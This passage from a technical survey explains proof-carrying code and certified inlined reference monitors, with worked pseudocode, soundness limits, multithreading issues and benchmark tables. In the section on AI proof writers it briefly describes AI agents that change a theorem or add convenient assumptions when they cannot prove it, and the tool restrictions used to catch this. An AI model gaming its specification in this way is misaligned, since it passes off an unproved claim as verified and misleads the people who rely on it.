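A receiver that runs Cheko has to do the whole analysis itself, which took half an hour on average, and the next receiver of the same program has to repeat it. With proof-carrying code, the producer finds a proof that the program obeys the policy and ships it with the program. Each receiver only checks the proof, which is much easier than finding one. For example, a loop invariant may take a long time to discover, but once the producer has written it down, a receiver only has to confirm that it holds at the start and that one pass through the loop preserves it.

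### Proof-carrying code in an operating system kernel

In *Safe Kernel Extensions Without Run-Time Checking*, Necula and Lee (1996) wanted an operating system kernel to run small programs from untrusted users. Their main examples were packet filters, which select the network packets that an application receives. The kernel publishes a safety policy with three parts: a precondition that the kernel guarantees whenever it starts a user's program, a procedure that turns any program into a logical formula, and the axioms that a proof of this formula may use.

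A toy service from the paper shows how this works. The kernel gives the program the address r of a table entry. The word at r is a tag, and the word at r + 8 holds data. The program may read both words, but it may write the data only if the tag is not 0. A user might supply this program:

```
1  tag = memory[r]
2  if tag == 0: goto 4
3  memory[r + 8] = new_value
4  return
```

The kernel's procedure starts at the end and works backwards, asking what must be true before each line:

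- Line 4 requires nothing.
- Line 3 requires r + 8 to be writable.
- Line 2 requires r + 8 to be writable if `tag` is not 0.
- Line 1 requires r to be readable, and r + 8 to be writable if the word at r is not 0.

The kernel's precondition guarantees the last of these conditions, so the program is safe. Each condition is the *weakest precondition* of the code from that line on, the least demanding condition under which that code runs safely. If an assignment x = e must make a condition Q true, its weakest precondition is Q[e/x], which is Q with e in place of x. The weakest precondition of a test combines one condition for each branch.

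The real packet filters took 1 to 3 milliseconds to check and then ran without any run-time checks. None of them contained loops, and a prototype found all their proofs automatically. Necula and Lee still considered automating proof writing one of the most serious obstacles to practical use. They noted that a producer could simplify a hard proof by inserting an extra run-time check, though their examples never needed one. An inlined monitor consists of such checks, so it should be a good candidate for a shipped proof.

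### A monitor that never runs

In 2008, Aktug and colleagues worked out what a proof about an inlined monitor should state. They add a *ghost monitor* to the program, a second reference monitor that exists only in the proof annotations and never runs. It starts in the initial state of the policy's automaton. At each call or return that the policy covers, an annotation updates its state with the automaton's transition function. If the policy forbids the event, the state becomes ⊥, an error value.

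The ghost state is therefore a copy of the policy state that formulas can mention. Aktug and colleagues proved that a program adheres to the policy if and only if these annotations are valid, meaning that the ghost state is never ⊥ just before an event. Proving this directly can be as hard as proving any other fact about a program. But if the program contains a correct monitor, it is enough to show that the monitor state equals the ghost state at every method call and return. No program variable can hold ⊥, so if the two states are equal, the ghost state isn't ⊥.

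This invariant also lets a checker examine one method at a time, if each method updates the monitor state for its own calls. Aktug and colleagues knew of no general-purpose rewriter that violated this condition.

Dam and Lundblad (2010), in *A Proof Carrying Code Framework for Inlined Reference Monitors in Java Bytecode*, built a working system for mobile phones on this basis. It works as follows:

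1. The developer chooses a *contract*, a ConSpec policy that the program promises to obey, and a rewriter inserts a monitor for it.
2. A proof generator writes an assertion for each instruction. These assertions are the proof, and the developer ships them with the program and the contract.
3. The phone compares the contract with its own policy. Every trace that the contract allows must also be one that the policy allows.
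4. The phone adds the ghost monitor for the contract to the program.
5. The phone checks that the assertions fit the instructions and the ghost updates.

The phone adds the ghost monitor itself, so a developer cannot substitute a weaker policy. Suppose the phone's policy allows ten emails, and the developer inserts a monitor that allows a hundred. If the contract also allows a hundred, it fails the comparison in step 3. If the contract allows only ten, the phone's ghost monitor goes to ⊥ at the eleventh email, and no set of assertions can show that the inserted monitor agrees with it.

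For step 5, let m be the monitor state, g the ghost state and Ψ the invariant m = g. Let A_L be the assertion before instruction L, and wp(L) the weakest precondition that the phone calculates for that instruction from the assertions that follow it. For each method, the phone checks two things:

- Ψ ⇒ A₀
- A_L ⇒ wp(L) for every instruction L

For a return instruction, wp(L) is Ψ. Each method can thus assume the invariant when it starts and must restore it before it returns.

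### Working backwards from a network connection

The published example is a policy that forbids a program to send data over the network after it has read the phone's memory. Let state 0 mean "memory not read" and state 1 "memory read". Without the instructions that copy arguments, the inserted code looks like this:

```
1  if m == 0: goto 3
2  exit
   [ghost: if g == 0, keep g; otherwise g = ⊥]
3  open the network connection
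```

The line in brackets is the phone's ghost update. Working backwards from the call gives these assertions:

| Point in the code | Assertion | Reason |
|---|---|---|
| Before line 3 | m = g | The invariant must hold at every call |
| Before the ghost update | If g = 0, then m = g; otherwise m = ⊥ | This puts the new value of g into m = g |
| Before line 2 | True | Nothing runs after the exit |
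| Before line 1 | If m = 0, the assertion before the ghost update; otherwise true | The test leads to one of two places |

The code before this block guarantees m = g, so the phone has to show that m = g implies the assertion before line 1. If m is not 0, the assertion is true. If m is 0, then g is also 0, and the assertion reduces to m = g, which already holds.

If the developer leaves out the guard, m = g has to imply the assertion that precedes the ghost update by itself. The implication fails when m and g are both 1, because the assertion then requires m = ⊥, so the phone rejects the program.

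The same calculation catches the fault from the first section, in which an optimizer deletes the line that records a read. Suppose the ghost monitor sets g to 1 when the read returns. For the invariant m = g to hold after that update, m must be 1 before it. With the line `m = 1` in place, the requirement becomes 1 = 1. Without that line, the only available assumption before the update is m = g, which doesn't imply m = 1.

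### Why the rest of the program needs no proof

The inserted blocks are a small part of the program. For every instruction outside them, the generator uses m = g as the assertion, and the phone has to confirm that the instruction can't make that assertion false.

A syntactic check is enough for this because the rewriter stores the monitor's state, m, in a static field of a new class. It declares the class `final`, so no other class can extend it. In Java bytecode, only the `putstatic` instruction changes a static field, and the instruction names the field. The phone therefore looks for instructions outside the inserted blocks that write to this field. If there are none, ordinary code can't affect m, and it can't affect g because g isn't in the program.

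Ordinary code might still jump into the middle of a block to avoid the guard, but the proof would then have to show that the assertion at the destination holds. In the example, only m = g is known when code jumps to the point just before the ghost update. That isn't enough to prove the assertion there, so the phone rejects the program.

Cheko scans unmarked code for much the same reason. Another benefit, Dam and Lundblad point out, is that the checker needs a detailed model of only the instructions that rewriters insert. If a new version of Java adds an instruction, someone only has to confirm that it leaves static fields alone.

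### How the phone checks a proof quickly

Whether one formula implies another is undecidable in general, even when the assertions are given. The proofs for inserted monitors have a form that avoids this problem. Most of the checks compare a formula with itself, and each block has only one nontrivial check, at its first instruction, where m = g must imply the calculated weakest precondition.

The phone does this check by replacing both m and g with a new name, z. Suppose a policy counts emails and the monitor adds 1 to its count. The check then includes an equation such as m + 1 = g + 1, which becomes z + 1 = z + 1. Both sides are identical, so the phone can replace the equation with "true". Each replacement takes time proportional to the length of the formula and doesn't make the formula longer, so the total time is polynomial in the size of the program.

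The theorem about checking time assumes that two expressions count as equal only if they have the same form. If a rewriter inserted `1 + m` where the policy has `g + 1`, the phone would need a rule of arithmetic to verify that they are equal. A checker can include some of these rules, but the theorem does not cover arbitrary arithmetic.

Dam and Lundblad also proved that every program their example rewriter produces can ship with a proof, and that the generator finds this proof in polynomial time. Developers can use other rewriters and optimize one call for speed and another for size.

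### Two applications on a 2000s phone

They tested the system on two applications. MobileJam reports traffic jams, and its policy allowed connections only to Yahoo's map service. Snake, a game that can send the player's score to a server, was given the policy about phone memory. A desktop computer inserted the monitors and generated the proofs, and a Sony Ericsson W810i phone checked them.

| | MobileJam | Snake |
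|---|---|---|
| Calls that the policy covers | 4 | 2 |
| Original size | 428.0 kb | 43.7 kb |
| Added by the monitor | 4.8 kb | 1.1 kb |
| Added by the proof | 20.6 kb | 2.6 kb |
| Inserting the monitor | 10.1 s | 8.6 s |
| Generating the proof | 4.7 s | 0.8 s |
| Checking the proof on the phone | 98 ms | 117 ms |

The proofs were larger than the monitors but increased the applications' size by only 5 to 6%. DCIL's proofs added far more, though its policies were also much richer. Checking took about a tenth of a second, whereas Cheko needed at least 35 seconds for every program, even on a much faster laptop.

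Two applications are too few to show how the checking time grows. Snake is about a tenth of MobileJam's size and has half as many relevant calls, yet its proof took slightly longer to check, for reasons left unexplained. The paper also reports no tests with faulty monitors or forged proofs.

### What the Coq proof covers

Dam and Lundblad formalized the soundness argument in Coq. The argument first shows that if all the local checks succeed, the assertions hold in every run, and then that if the assertions hold in every run, the program follows its contract. Lundblad and Palmskog (2020) released a version of the formalization, *PCC*, for Coq 8.10 and later. The proof covers the method but not the code of the phone's checker, so a programming mistake there could still let a bad program through.

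The paper's printed rule for method calls requires the invariant before a call but places no requirement on the assertion after it. Taken literally, this would let a dishonest developer write "false" as the assertion after the first call in a method. Anything follows from a false assumption, so every later check in that method would succeed regardless of the code. The proofs from Dam and Lundblad's generator put the invariant after the call, which is justified because every method restores it before returning. A sound checker must require this of every proof, and the rule in the Coq version presumably does.

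The framework has several other limits:

- It covers programs with one thread. Dam, Jacobs and colleagues (2014), in *Security monitor inlining and certification for multithreaded Java*, later took up programs with several.
- Like the earlier work by Aktug and colleagues, it excludes reflection and treats each library call as a single, unpredictable step. The model even allows a library call to change anything in memory, although the syntactic check depends on such calls leaving the monitor's field alone.
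- It keeps one history for the whole run. A separate limit for each file would require the proof to track references to objects, as Mobile's types do.
- It assumes that inserted code does not throw unexpected exceptions. This is the kind of exception that Cheko's developers found could disable a monitor in vrenamer. Dam and Lundblad say that they could remove the assumption by making the inserted code more complicated.

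### CertiBlock: a certificate without a proof

*Certificate-Carrying Transformation of Event-Driven Block Programs* (Si and Zhang, 2026) presents CertiBlock, a system that optimizes programs in Scratch, a language in which children build games from blocks. Its checker has to establish that an optimization leaves the player's experience unchanged, not that the program obeys a security policy. The problem of trust is the same as with inlined reference monitors, because a large, untrusted tool rewrites a program and a separate checker accepts or rejects the result.

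The optimizer sends a certificate with each change, but the certificate contains no proof. It states what kind of change the optimizer made, where it made it, and which observer should notice no difference. It also contains digests, short codes calculated from the old and new files. The checker then does the following:

1. It recalculates the digests, to confirm that the certificate belongs to these two files.
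2. It looks up the conditions for this kind of change in its own fixed list.
3. It works out from the two programs whether every condition holds, including that nothing else has changed.
4. It accepts the change only if all the conditions hold. Any error or unfamiliar block leads to a rejection.

Suppose a game moves a character to the centre of the screen and then immediately to the left edge, and the optimizer proposes to delete the first move. Scratch runs a script without interruption until it reaches certain blocks, such as a wait, and draws the screen only between these stretches. If both moves are in the same stretch, the player never sees the character at the centre. The checker therefore looks for a wait between the moves and for anything else that could reveal the first position, such as a drawing pen that leaves a line or a block that copies the character. Si and Zhang proved in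 Lean, another program that checks proofs, that deleting an overwritten change is safe if nothing observes it in between.

CertiBlock's checker accepted at least one change in 283 of 300 real projects, and checking took less than a tenth of a second per project on average. Most of the accepted changes removed unused images, sounds or variables. In another test, a simpler tool that ignored the special conditions deleted 79 moves or other visual changes. Running the projects showed that 18 of these deletions altered what the player saw, and the checker rejected all 18.

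Recalculating everything requires a large checker. It has 9,921 lines, compared with 3,060 for the optimizer, and must account for every way a change could become visible. An audit found eight bad changes that the checker had accepted even though all of its tests passed. In one, the optimizer removed an unused costume from a character. This renumbered the later costumes, and another character was displaying one of those numbers on the screen. Si and Zhang fixed all eight faults, and the checker then rejected all 4,278 deliberately altered changes in a further test. The Lean proof could not have prevented the faults because it covers a mathematical model, and the working checker is a separate Python program.

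Dam and Lundblad's checker needs less of this knowledge, because the policy defines what counts as a violation and the checker needs rules only for the instructions in the inserted blocks. But it requires a producer who can write a proof.

### AI models that write proofs about programs

Producers can now get much more help writing these proofs from AI models, which work in languages such as Lean and Coq. The receiver doesn't need to trust the model because the proof checker examines every step. The best-known results are in mathematics, where numbers can be treated as unlimited. Proofs about programs involve different work, such as showing that no sum exceeds 64 bits, that no index runs past the end of a list, or that every loop finishes.

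Ganguly, Raghunathan and colleagues (2026), in *Scaling Lean Theorem Proving for Real-World Code Verification*, measured both kinds of proof with one system, EasyProver. It runs many copies of Anthropic's Fable 5 model, which divide a proof into parts and try different approaches. These are some of its results:

| Task | Result |
|---|---|
| Problems from the Putnam mathematics competition | 669 of 672 proved |
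| Verification conditions from industrial software | 588 of 600 proved, 9 more disproved |
| Statements about Rust programs translated into Lean | 1,054 of 2,000 proved |

The second row is the closest to proof-carrying code, because a verification condition is the kind of formula a receiver calculates from a program. For the last row, AI agents wrote Rust solutions to programming exercises, a tool translated them into Lean, and another agent wrote statements about them. Given 30 minutes for each statement, EasyProver proved 67% of those about easy exercises and 38% of those about hard ones.

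One of the Rust programs sorts the numbers in even positions in ascending order and those in odd positions in descending order. The proof establishes only that the program finishes without an error and returns a list of the same length, not that it sorts correctly. The program has 67 lines, its Lean translation has 281, and the file with the finished proof has 336. Most of the proof consists of facts about the six loops, such as how many numbers each list contains after a given number of passes. EasyProver failed to prove that a 66-line merge sort always finishes without an error.

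Results vary with the task and the proof language. *Harnessing Code Agents for Automatic Software Verification* (2026) describes Aria, a system that guides an ordinary coding agent. Aria proved all 217 lemmas it attempted from RustBelt, a Coq project about the safety of Rust's standard library.

Dafny and Verus, which *AlgoVeri* (2026) contrasts with Lean, need less detailed proofs than Lean does. The programmer supplies invariants and other hints, and an automatic solver tries to complete the proof. *Automating Formal Verification with Reinforcement Learning and Recursive Inference* (2026) reports a test in which models had to restore missing hints in Dafny programs. The best model succeeded on about 89% of the programs, and about 96% were solved by at least one model. This style suits shipped proofs less well, because the receiver has to run and trust a solver that may run out of time.

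### Who chooses the statement

How useful a proof is depends on the statement it proves. In *SWE-Proof*, Ma, Mikek and colleagues (2026) asked Claude Opus 4.8 to fix 500 real software bugs. Without formal methods, 85% of its fixes passed the tests. Asking the model to write a formal specification and prove that its fix met it made almost no difference, but when the researchers supplied a correct specification, 94 to 96% of the fixes passed. Only 56% of the specifications that the model wrote from the bug reports alone passed an audit. The rest usually left out part of the required behaviour.

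Policy adherence largely avoids this difficulty because the receiver already has a policy, and the ghost monitor turns it into an exact statement about any program. People can still write the wrong policy, as the earlier examples from ConSpec and SPoX showed, but nobody has to guess what each new program should do.

Having the receiver set the statement to be proved also stops the producer from changing it to make the proof easier. An AI agent that can't prove a theorem may change the theorem or add a convenient assumption. EasyProver therefore lets the model edit only the proof and allows only assumptions on a fixed list. *ProsaBuddy* (2026), a system for proofs about real-time scheduling, checks after each attempt that the statement is unchanged and that the agent has proved it. In Dam and Lundblad's framework, the phone builds the statement itself from the program and the phone's own policy.

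### What cheaper proofs would change

Dam and Lundblad kept proof writing easy by requiring the monitor state to equal the ghost state at every call. Like Cheko's SYNC condition, this rules out the safe monitor from the previous section that tests once that `s` is at most 7, sends three emails in a loop and only then adds 3 to `s`. Aktug and colleagues' original condition is less strict, since it requires only that the ghost state never becomes ⊥. Let i be the number of emails that the loop has sent. A proof could use the invariant

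g = s + i, with s ≤ 7 and i ≤ 3

Before each email, i is at most 2, so g is at most 9 and the policy allows the email. After the loop, i is 3, and the update makes `s` equal to g again. Checking this takes a few lines of arithmetic, but finding the invariant is harder. An AI model might find the invariant, and might also find proofs for monitors that keep their counts in a hash table, which Cheko cannot certify. None of these AI studies tested inlined monitors, so a model's success rate on them is unknown.

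AI models also make it more practical to prove the rewriter itself correct, which Hamlen thought in 2006 might be far off. *Machine-Generated, Machine-Checked Proofs for a Verified Compiler (Experience Report)* (2026) describes how Claude Code, running Claude Opus 4.6, developed a correctness proof for one stage of a compiler. The researchers gave general guidance and reviewed the result, but seldom had to explain the reasoning. If a model can also repair such a proof whenever the rewriter changes, the proof need not go out of date. Proving the rewriter correct would still leave the problem of rewriting by third parties, which shipping a proof with the finished program avoids.

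Analysis at the receiver still has the clear advantage of needing less cooperation from the producer. Plenty of code will arrive without a proof. A receiver could ask an AI model to write the missing proof, but the receiver would then be doing the slow search for a proof itself again, and the search might fail.

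## Checking that permitted behaviour survives rewriting

A rewriter that turned every program into `halt` would pass any adherence check. A more likely fault is a monitor for the ten-email limit that stops the program at the ninth email, and it would pass too. Ruling out such faults requires a separate proof of transparency, the property that permitted behaviour survives rewriting.

Dam and Lundblad leave transparency out of their certificates because they consider it a matter for the particular rewriter. That is reasonable where the developer inserts the monitor and can test the application before shipping it, but less so where a distributor rewrites other people's programs in bulk. *Hippocratic Binary Instrumentation* (Sridhar, Wartell and Hamlen, 2013) reports that advertising networks worry about malicious advertisements but often refuse any protection that modifies the code, unless they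 see overwhelming evidence that safe advertisements will still work. Even a temporary fault in a few advertisements could cost millions of dollars. The fear has some basis, because a monitor that works in most programs can malfunction in an unusual one, such as one that overrides a system method the monitor calls.

### Running two programs side by side

Sridhar and colleagues built FlashTrack, the first automatic transparency checker for inlined monitors. It compares an original ActionScript program with its rewritten version. Chudnov and Naumann had earlier proved by hand that one rewriter was transparent, but their proof does not carry over to other rewriters.

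No algorithm can decide whether two arbitrary programs behave alike, but comparing a program with its rewritten version is easier because the rewriter leaves most of the program alone and confines its changes to small blocks. Compiler researchers use a similar technique, called translation validation, to confirm that an optimization has preserved a program's behaviour. Unlike an optimizer, a monitor has to change the runs that break the policy. FlashTrack therefore proves that if a run of the original program complies with the policy, the rewritten program behaves the same way on the same input.

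Here is a version of the researchers' own example, in which an advertisement may redirect the browser at most 100 times. The original program is:

```
1  wait for a click
2  navigate(address)
3  goto 1
```

The rewriter adds a counter `c`, which starts at 0:

```
1  wait for a click
2  if c < 100: goto 4
3  exit
4  navigate(address)
5  c = c + 1
6  goto 1
```

Let A be the policy state, which here is the number of redirects so far. FlashTrack starts with both programs at line 1, where their traces are equal and c = A. It then reasons as follows:

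1. Both programs wait for the same click.
2. The original program is about to redirect. FlashTrack considers only runs in which this redirect complies with the policy, so A is at most 99.
3. Since c = A, `c` is also at most 99. The guard passes, and the rewritten program cannot reach `exit`.
4. Both programs redirect to the same address, so their traces are still equal. A and `c` both go up by 1, so c = A again.
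5. Both programs return to line 1, in a situation that the starting description already covers. FlashTrack accepts the pair.

If the guard were `c < 99`, the rewritten program would exit at the hundredth redirect, even though the policy allows that redirect. FlashTrack would reject this monitor, and an adherence certifier would accept it. A guard of `c < 101` would have the opposite result, because it is transparent, never interfering with a compliant run, but lets through a forbidden redirect.

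The published example contains a mismatch of this second sort. In the 2014 version of the paper, Sridhar and colleagues describe the policy's automaton as having states 0 to 99 and moving up one state with each redirect. That automaton permits only 99 redirects, while the instruction in the printed guard permits 100. FlashTrack could accept this pair, but an adherence certifier would have to reject the monitor.

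### What counts as the same behaviour

FlashTrack compares sequences of observable events, which are most calls to the system's programming interface, along with their arguments, because an ActionScript program has no other way to affect the display or the file system. A policy can exempt calls that are known to have no effect. The comparison ignores timing, so a monitor can be transparent even if it slows the program down.

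The rewritten program has extra instructions to execute, so the two programs don't stay synchronised. If the original ran twice as fast, its trace would always be longer, even with a perfect monitor. The formal definition therefore lets the checker choose how to interleave the two runs. An interleaving is *progressive* if both programs keep taking steps, where a finished program counts as repeating its last state for ever. Two interleavings are *shuffles* of each other if each program takes the same steps in the same order in both. A rewritten program is transparent if every progressive interleaving of compliant runs has a shuffle in which the two traces are equal infinitely often.

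The words "infinitely often" rule out a monitor that postpones the program's work for ever. Checking an infinite run directly would be impossible, so FlashTrack looks for a set S of descriptions of the paired programs with three properties:

- S includes the starting situation.
- The two traces are equal in every member of S.
- From any member of S, every compliant continuation has a shuffle that reaches a member of S again.

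By induction, the traces then become equal repeatedly throughout the run. In the example, S can be the set of situations where both programs are at line 1, their traces are equal, and c = A.

Each rewriter comes with an *invariant generator*, a program of about 100 lines that gives FlashTrack hints for finding S. For each pair of points in the two programs, it suggests a simpler description of the situation, the later points where the traces should be equal again, and a limit on the steps needed to reach them. Outside the blocks that the rewriter changed, the suggested description is that the two programs agree on everything they share and that the monitor state equals the policy state, much like Cheko's SYNC. Inside a changed block, FlashTrack keeps all its information and follows every path to the exit. FlashTrack checks every hint, so a bad one can make it reject a harmless monitor but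 not accept a harmful one.

Programs that inspect themselves need special treatment. An applet that prints its own size changes observably after rewriting, because it prints a larger number. Sridhar and colleagues treat the size as an input, so they require only that the applet still prints the size it finds. An applet may also detect the monitor and disable features that would conflict with the policy.

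### Tests on Flash advertisements

Sridhar and colleagues tested FlashTrack on 27 advertisements from public websites and one attack program that they wrote themselves. For 24 of the advertisements, the policy limited the number of redirects. The other policies limited cookies, stopped an advertisement from expanding over the page, and limited how many bytes a program could write into memory. The memory limit defended against heap spraying, in which a program fills memory with harmful code for another program to trigger.

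These are some of the results, with times in milliseconds:

| Program | Policy | Original size | Methods | Rewriting | Checking |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| wines | redirects | 185 KB | 926 | 904 | 35,926 |
| lowes | redirects | 34 KB | 181 | 218 | 16,549 |
| prius | redirects | 71 KB | 554 | 516 | 10,359 |
| sprite | redirects | 34 KB | 324 | 234 | 3,075 |
| jlopez | redirects | 17 KB | 151 | 95 | 560 |
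| expandall | expansion | 3 KB | 17 | 47 | 79 |
| cookie | cookies | 3 KB | 8 | 31 | 16 |
| HeapSprAttk | memory writes | 1 KB | 4 | 15 | 15 |

Sixteen of the 28 programs took less than a tenth of a second to check. The slowest, an interactive menu of wines, took 36 seconds, about 40 times as long as rewriting it. Size alone doesn't explain the times, since `lowes` and `sprite` are equally large but one took five times as long as the other. The monitor stopped the heap-spraying attack, and FlashTrack verified that enforcing the same policy didn't change the behaviour of any other program.

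Sridhar and colleagues knew of no case in which FlashTrack wrongly rejected their rewriters' output, even when a rewriter had optimized the code by merging some of the program's own branches with the monitor's into a single multi-way jump. FlashTrack also caught bugs while they were developing the rewriters. Some monitors threw uncaught exceptions, some damaged a value that the program later used, and some accidentally triggered start-up code with visible effects. Sridhar and colleagues don't report the number of bugs, and they didn't test FlashTrack systematically on faulty monitors.

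FlashTrack rejects monitors that keep their state in a hash table, for the same reason Cheko does. It also rejects any monitor that adds a nontrivial loop to a compliant run, because it can't show that the loop ends. It can handle the program's own loops because it only has to show that the monitor hasn't changed their exit conditions.

Runs that break the policy are exempt from the whole comparison. Suppose a game saves the player's progress and later tries to send an eleventh email. The definition of transparency does not require the rewritten game to save that progress, even though saving it was harmless. Sridhar and colleagues suggest extending the checker to protect behaviour up to the violation.

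### Locks that remove permitted behaviour

ActionScript programs have a single thread, and Sridhar and colleagues described practical transparency checking for multithreaded bytecode as an open problem. Threads can also make adherence and transparency conflict, which is a more basic difficulty.

Dam, Jacobs and colleagues (2010), in *Provably correct inline monitoring for multithreaded Java-like programs*, define the relevant properties as relations between sets of traces. Let T(P) be the set of traces that program P can produce, Π the set that the policy allows, and I(P) the rewritten program. The rewriter is:

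- *secure* if T(I(P)) ⊆ Π, which is policy adherence
- *conservative* if T(I(P)) ⊆ T(P), so that it adds no behaviour
- *transparent* if T(P) ∩ Π ⊆ T(I(P)), so that it removes no permitted behaviour

A rewriter that always produces `halt` is secure and conservative but not transparent.

In a threaded program, the monitor needs a lock so that two threads can't pass the same guard at once. But the lock itself can remove behaviour, as in this program, where `event` is a short security-relevant method and both shared variables start at 0:

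```
thread 1:                 thread 2:
  before = 1                x = after
  event()                   event()
  after = 1                 y = before
                            if x == 1 and y == 0: event()
```

If every instruction took effect in the order written, the third call could never happen, because thread 2 could find `after` equal to 1 only if `before` was already 1. But Java allows the compiler and the processor to reorder such accesses when the threads don't synchronize, so the original program can make three calls. The monitor's lock around each call prevents the reordering, so the rewritten program can make only two calls, even if the policy allows three.

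Lundblad's thesis, *Inlined Reference Monitors*, concludes more generally that under Java's memory model no monitor can be both secure and completely transparent. Few people would miss the third call, which depends on a flaw in the program. Dam and colleagues consider transparency meaningful only for programs that synchronize their threads properly, and propose *strong conservativity* for the rest. It requires every complete trace of the rewritten program to be a complete trace of the original, cut off at the first violation if there is one. A monitor can pass this test even if it makes some permitted orderings impossible, but it fails if it stops a compliant program early.

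### What it costs to hold the lock

The 2010 rewriter takes the lock before each security-relevant call and keeps it until the call returns. This gives the monitor the exact order of these calls, and the rewriter is secure and conservative for any policy. Mobile similarly lets only one thread at a time use a monitored object.

Dam and colleagues measured the overhead on a Sony Ericsson W810i phone by calling an empty method a million times. The total time rose from 407 to 1,358 milliseconds, an increase of 951 nanoseconds per call. This excludes the time other threads spend waiting. If four threads each make a network call that takes a second, the program needs four seconds instead of one.

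The lock can also stop a program completely. Suppose two threads meet at a barrier, a method that doesn't return until both have called it. If the policy covers this method, the first thread holds the lock while it waits for the second, which can't enter the method without the lock. The proof of strong conservativity therefore assumes that security-relevant methods do not block in this way.

It also assumes that the Java virtual machine never throws an internal error, but the virtual machine can do so at almost any moment, including in the middle of a guard. The rewriter makes the program exit if anything other than the monitored call throws an exception inside the inserted code. This closes the kind of gap that Cheko found in vrenamer, but it can end a harmless run.

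### Which policies a threaded program can enforce

The alternative is to hold the lock only while the monitor checks and updates its state, and to release it during the call so that other threads can make their own calls. In their 2014 paper, Dam and colleagues proved exactly which policies allow a monitor that is both secure and transparent. They call these policies *race-free*, a term they had earlier described as meaning that the order of concurrent actions makes no difference to the policy.

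Each call and each return counts as a separate event. Inserted code runs just before a call and just after a return, so the monitor records a call slightly before it happens and a return slightly after. Events close together in different threads may therefore happen in a different order from the one recorded. The recorded order across threads is certain to be correct only when a return in one thread is recorded before a call in another.

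A policy is race-free, then, if for every trace it permits, it also permits every reordering that

- keeps the events of each thread in order, and
- keeps every return ahead of the calls in other threads that came after it.

Suppose a policy is not race-free, so that it permits some trace but forbids one of these reorderings. A transparent monitor must allow the permitted trace. But the threads could produce the forbidden trace by running the same inserted code in the same order, with only the timing of the real calls and returns slightly different. The monitor would have the same information in both runs, so it would have to allow both. It could prevent the forbidden trace only by making one thread wait for the other's call to return, which would also prevent the permitted trace, in which the calls overlap.

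In the other direction, suppose the policy is race-free and the monitor has recorded a permitted trace. The actual sequence of events is a reordering of that trace, so the policy permits it too. This half of the result presumably concerns properly synchronized programs, given the effect of locks on badly synchronized ones.

The limit of ten emails per run is race-free if the monitor counts calls, because reordering calls doesn't change how many there are. If the count is nine and two threads try to send, one takes the lock first and raises the count to ten, and the other can't send because the limit has been reached. Two threads can be inside `Mail.send` at the same time without harm.

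The rule against sending after reading a file is not race-free. Consider this run:

```
thread 2:  takes the lock, finds state = 0, releases the lock
thread 1:  takes the lock, sets state = 1, releases the lock
thread 1:  reads the file
thread 2:  sends
```

The monitor has recorded a send followed by a read, which the policy permits, but the program actually read before it sent. If the two threads share a buffer, the message could contain the file's contents. The recorded order can also differ from the actual order when an agent harness, the program that carries out an AI model's tool requests, runs several requests in parallel.

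A policy writer can sometimes bring a rule like this into the race-free class by making it stricter. The stricter rule could require every send to return before any read begins, and forbid sends from then on. This rule depends only on returns that precede calls, an order the monitor can reliably detect. The monitor would count the sends in progress and halt the program if it tried to read while that count was above zero. However, the stricter policy also forbids some harmless overlaps.

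A small change can also move a policy out of the class. Dam and colleagues' 2010 paper includes a contract that limits how many text messages a chess game may send, but adds to the count only when the sending method returns. Near the limit, whether a thread may start another message depends on whether an earlier call has just returned, and the monitor may register that return too late. Counting calls instead of returns would avoid the problem.

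### Certificates for threaded programs

A proof about a threaded program normally has to cover every way the threads can interleave. Dam and colleagues (2014) discuss how annotations could reduce the problem to sequential proofs about the inserted blocks alone. Cheko's constraint lists have no such method for handling other threads.

Dam and Lundblad explain the main condition: an assertion may mention only fields whose locks the thread holds at that point. For the email policy, let m be the monitor's count and g the ghost state, as in the previous section. An inserted block could look like this:

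```
lock
    if m >= 10: exit
    m = m + 1
    [ghost: if g < 10, g = g + 1; otherwise g = ⊥]
unlock
Mail.send()
```

The shared invariant is that m = g whenever no thread holds the lock. A thread can therefore assume m = g when it takes the lock, and it has to restore m = g before releasing it. No other thread can change m in between, so the receiver can check these lines as it would in a single-threaded program. If m is less than 10, so is g, and both go up by 1.

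The syntactic check from the previous section covers the rest of the program, but the receiver must also confirm that the inserted blocks use m only while holding the lock. Java guarantees that if threads always hold the same lock when they use a field, each read returns the most recent write. The reordering in the earlier example therefore cannot affect m.

In this block, the ghost update happens under the lock, not at the moment of sending. The proof therefore establishes that the recorded trace complies with the policy, but the real trace complies only if the policy is race-free. Holding the lock until the call returns removes that condition but brings back the waiting and the risk of deadlock. Neither kind of certificate establishes transparency, meaning that permitted behaviour survives rewriting.

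### Guarantees to ask for separately

Transparency and adherence together still leave room for a harmful rewriter. Suppose the policy covers only redirects, and the rewriter adds code that sets a tracking cookie whenever the monitor blocks one. An adherence certifier has no rule about cookies, and FlashTrack exempts runs that break the policy, so both would accept the program. Conservativity rules this out. Someone buying certified code should therefore ask about each of these guarantees by name:

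| Guarantee | Example of a fault it rules out | Available evidence |
|---|---|---|
| Policy adherence | The program sends an eleventh email | The certifiers in the previous sections |
| Transparency | The monitor stops the program at the ninth email | FlashTrack, for single-threaded Flash programs |
| Conservativity | The monitor sets a tracking cookie when it blocks a redirect | A proof about one rewriter by Dam and colleagues |
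| Strong conservativity | The monitor discards a saved game because of a later violation | The same proof, if the virtual machine throws no internal errors and monitored methods do not block |
| No new deadlocks | Two threads wait for each other at a barrier | The same proof, under the same assumptions |

For a threaded program, the buyer should also ask whether the monitor holds its lock during calls. If it does, the program's speed under a realistic load needs a separate test. If it does not, the buyer needs evidence that the policy is race-free.

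## What remains trusted, and how checkers themselves are verified

Certification removes the rewriter from the trusted computing base but adds a checker. The checker relies on a policy, a parser that reads the program, often a solver that decides logical questions, and a virtual machine that runs the program as expected. A mistake in any of them can let a forbidden program through.

### The trusted parts of four systems

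| | Mobile | ActionScript certifier | Cheko | Dam and Lundblad's phone checker |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Policy | allowed histories for each class | security automaton | SPoX | ConSpec |
| Parser | Microsoft's toolkit for .NET bytecode | Prolog, part of about 900 lines shared with the rewriters | part of 9,100 lines of Java | reads the bytecode and the proof |
| Checker | about 1,000 lines of OCaml | about 2,000 lines of Prolog | 5,200 lines of Prolog, plus event matching in the Java part | adds the ghost monitor and checks each assertion |
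| Solver | compares regular expressions | compares sets of traces | Prolog's linear constraint solver | simplifies formulas |
| Run-time code | about ten lines of C# for packages | `check_url`, for the redirect policy | none of its own | none of its own |
| Virtual machine | .NET | Flash | Java | Java |

The compilers and interpreters that run the checkers must also be trusted. Cheko needs a Java virtual machine, a Prolog system and a library that connects them. The ActionScript system also relies on a trusted tool that puts the certified bytecode back into the original Flash file after the check. If the tool inserted the wrong bytecode, the certificate would not apply to the program that users run.

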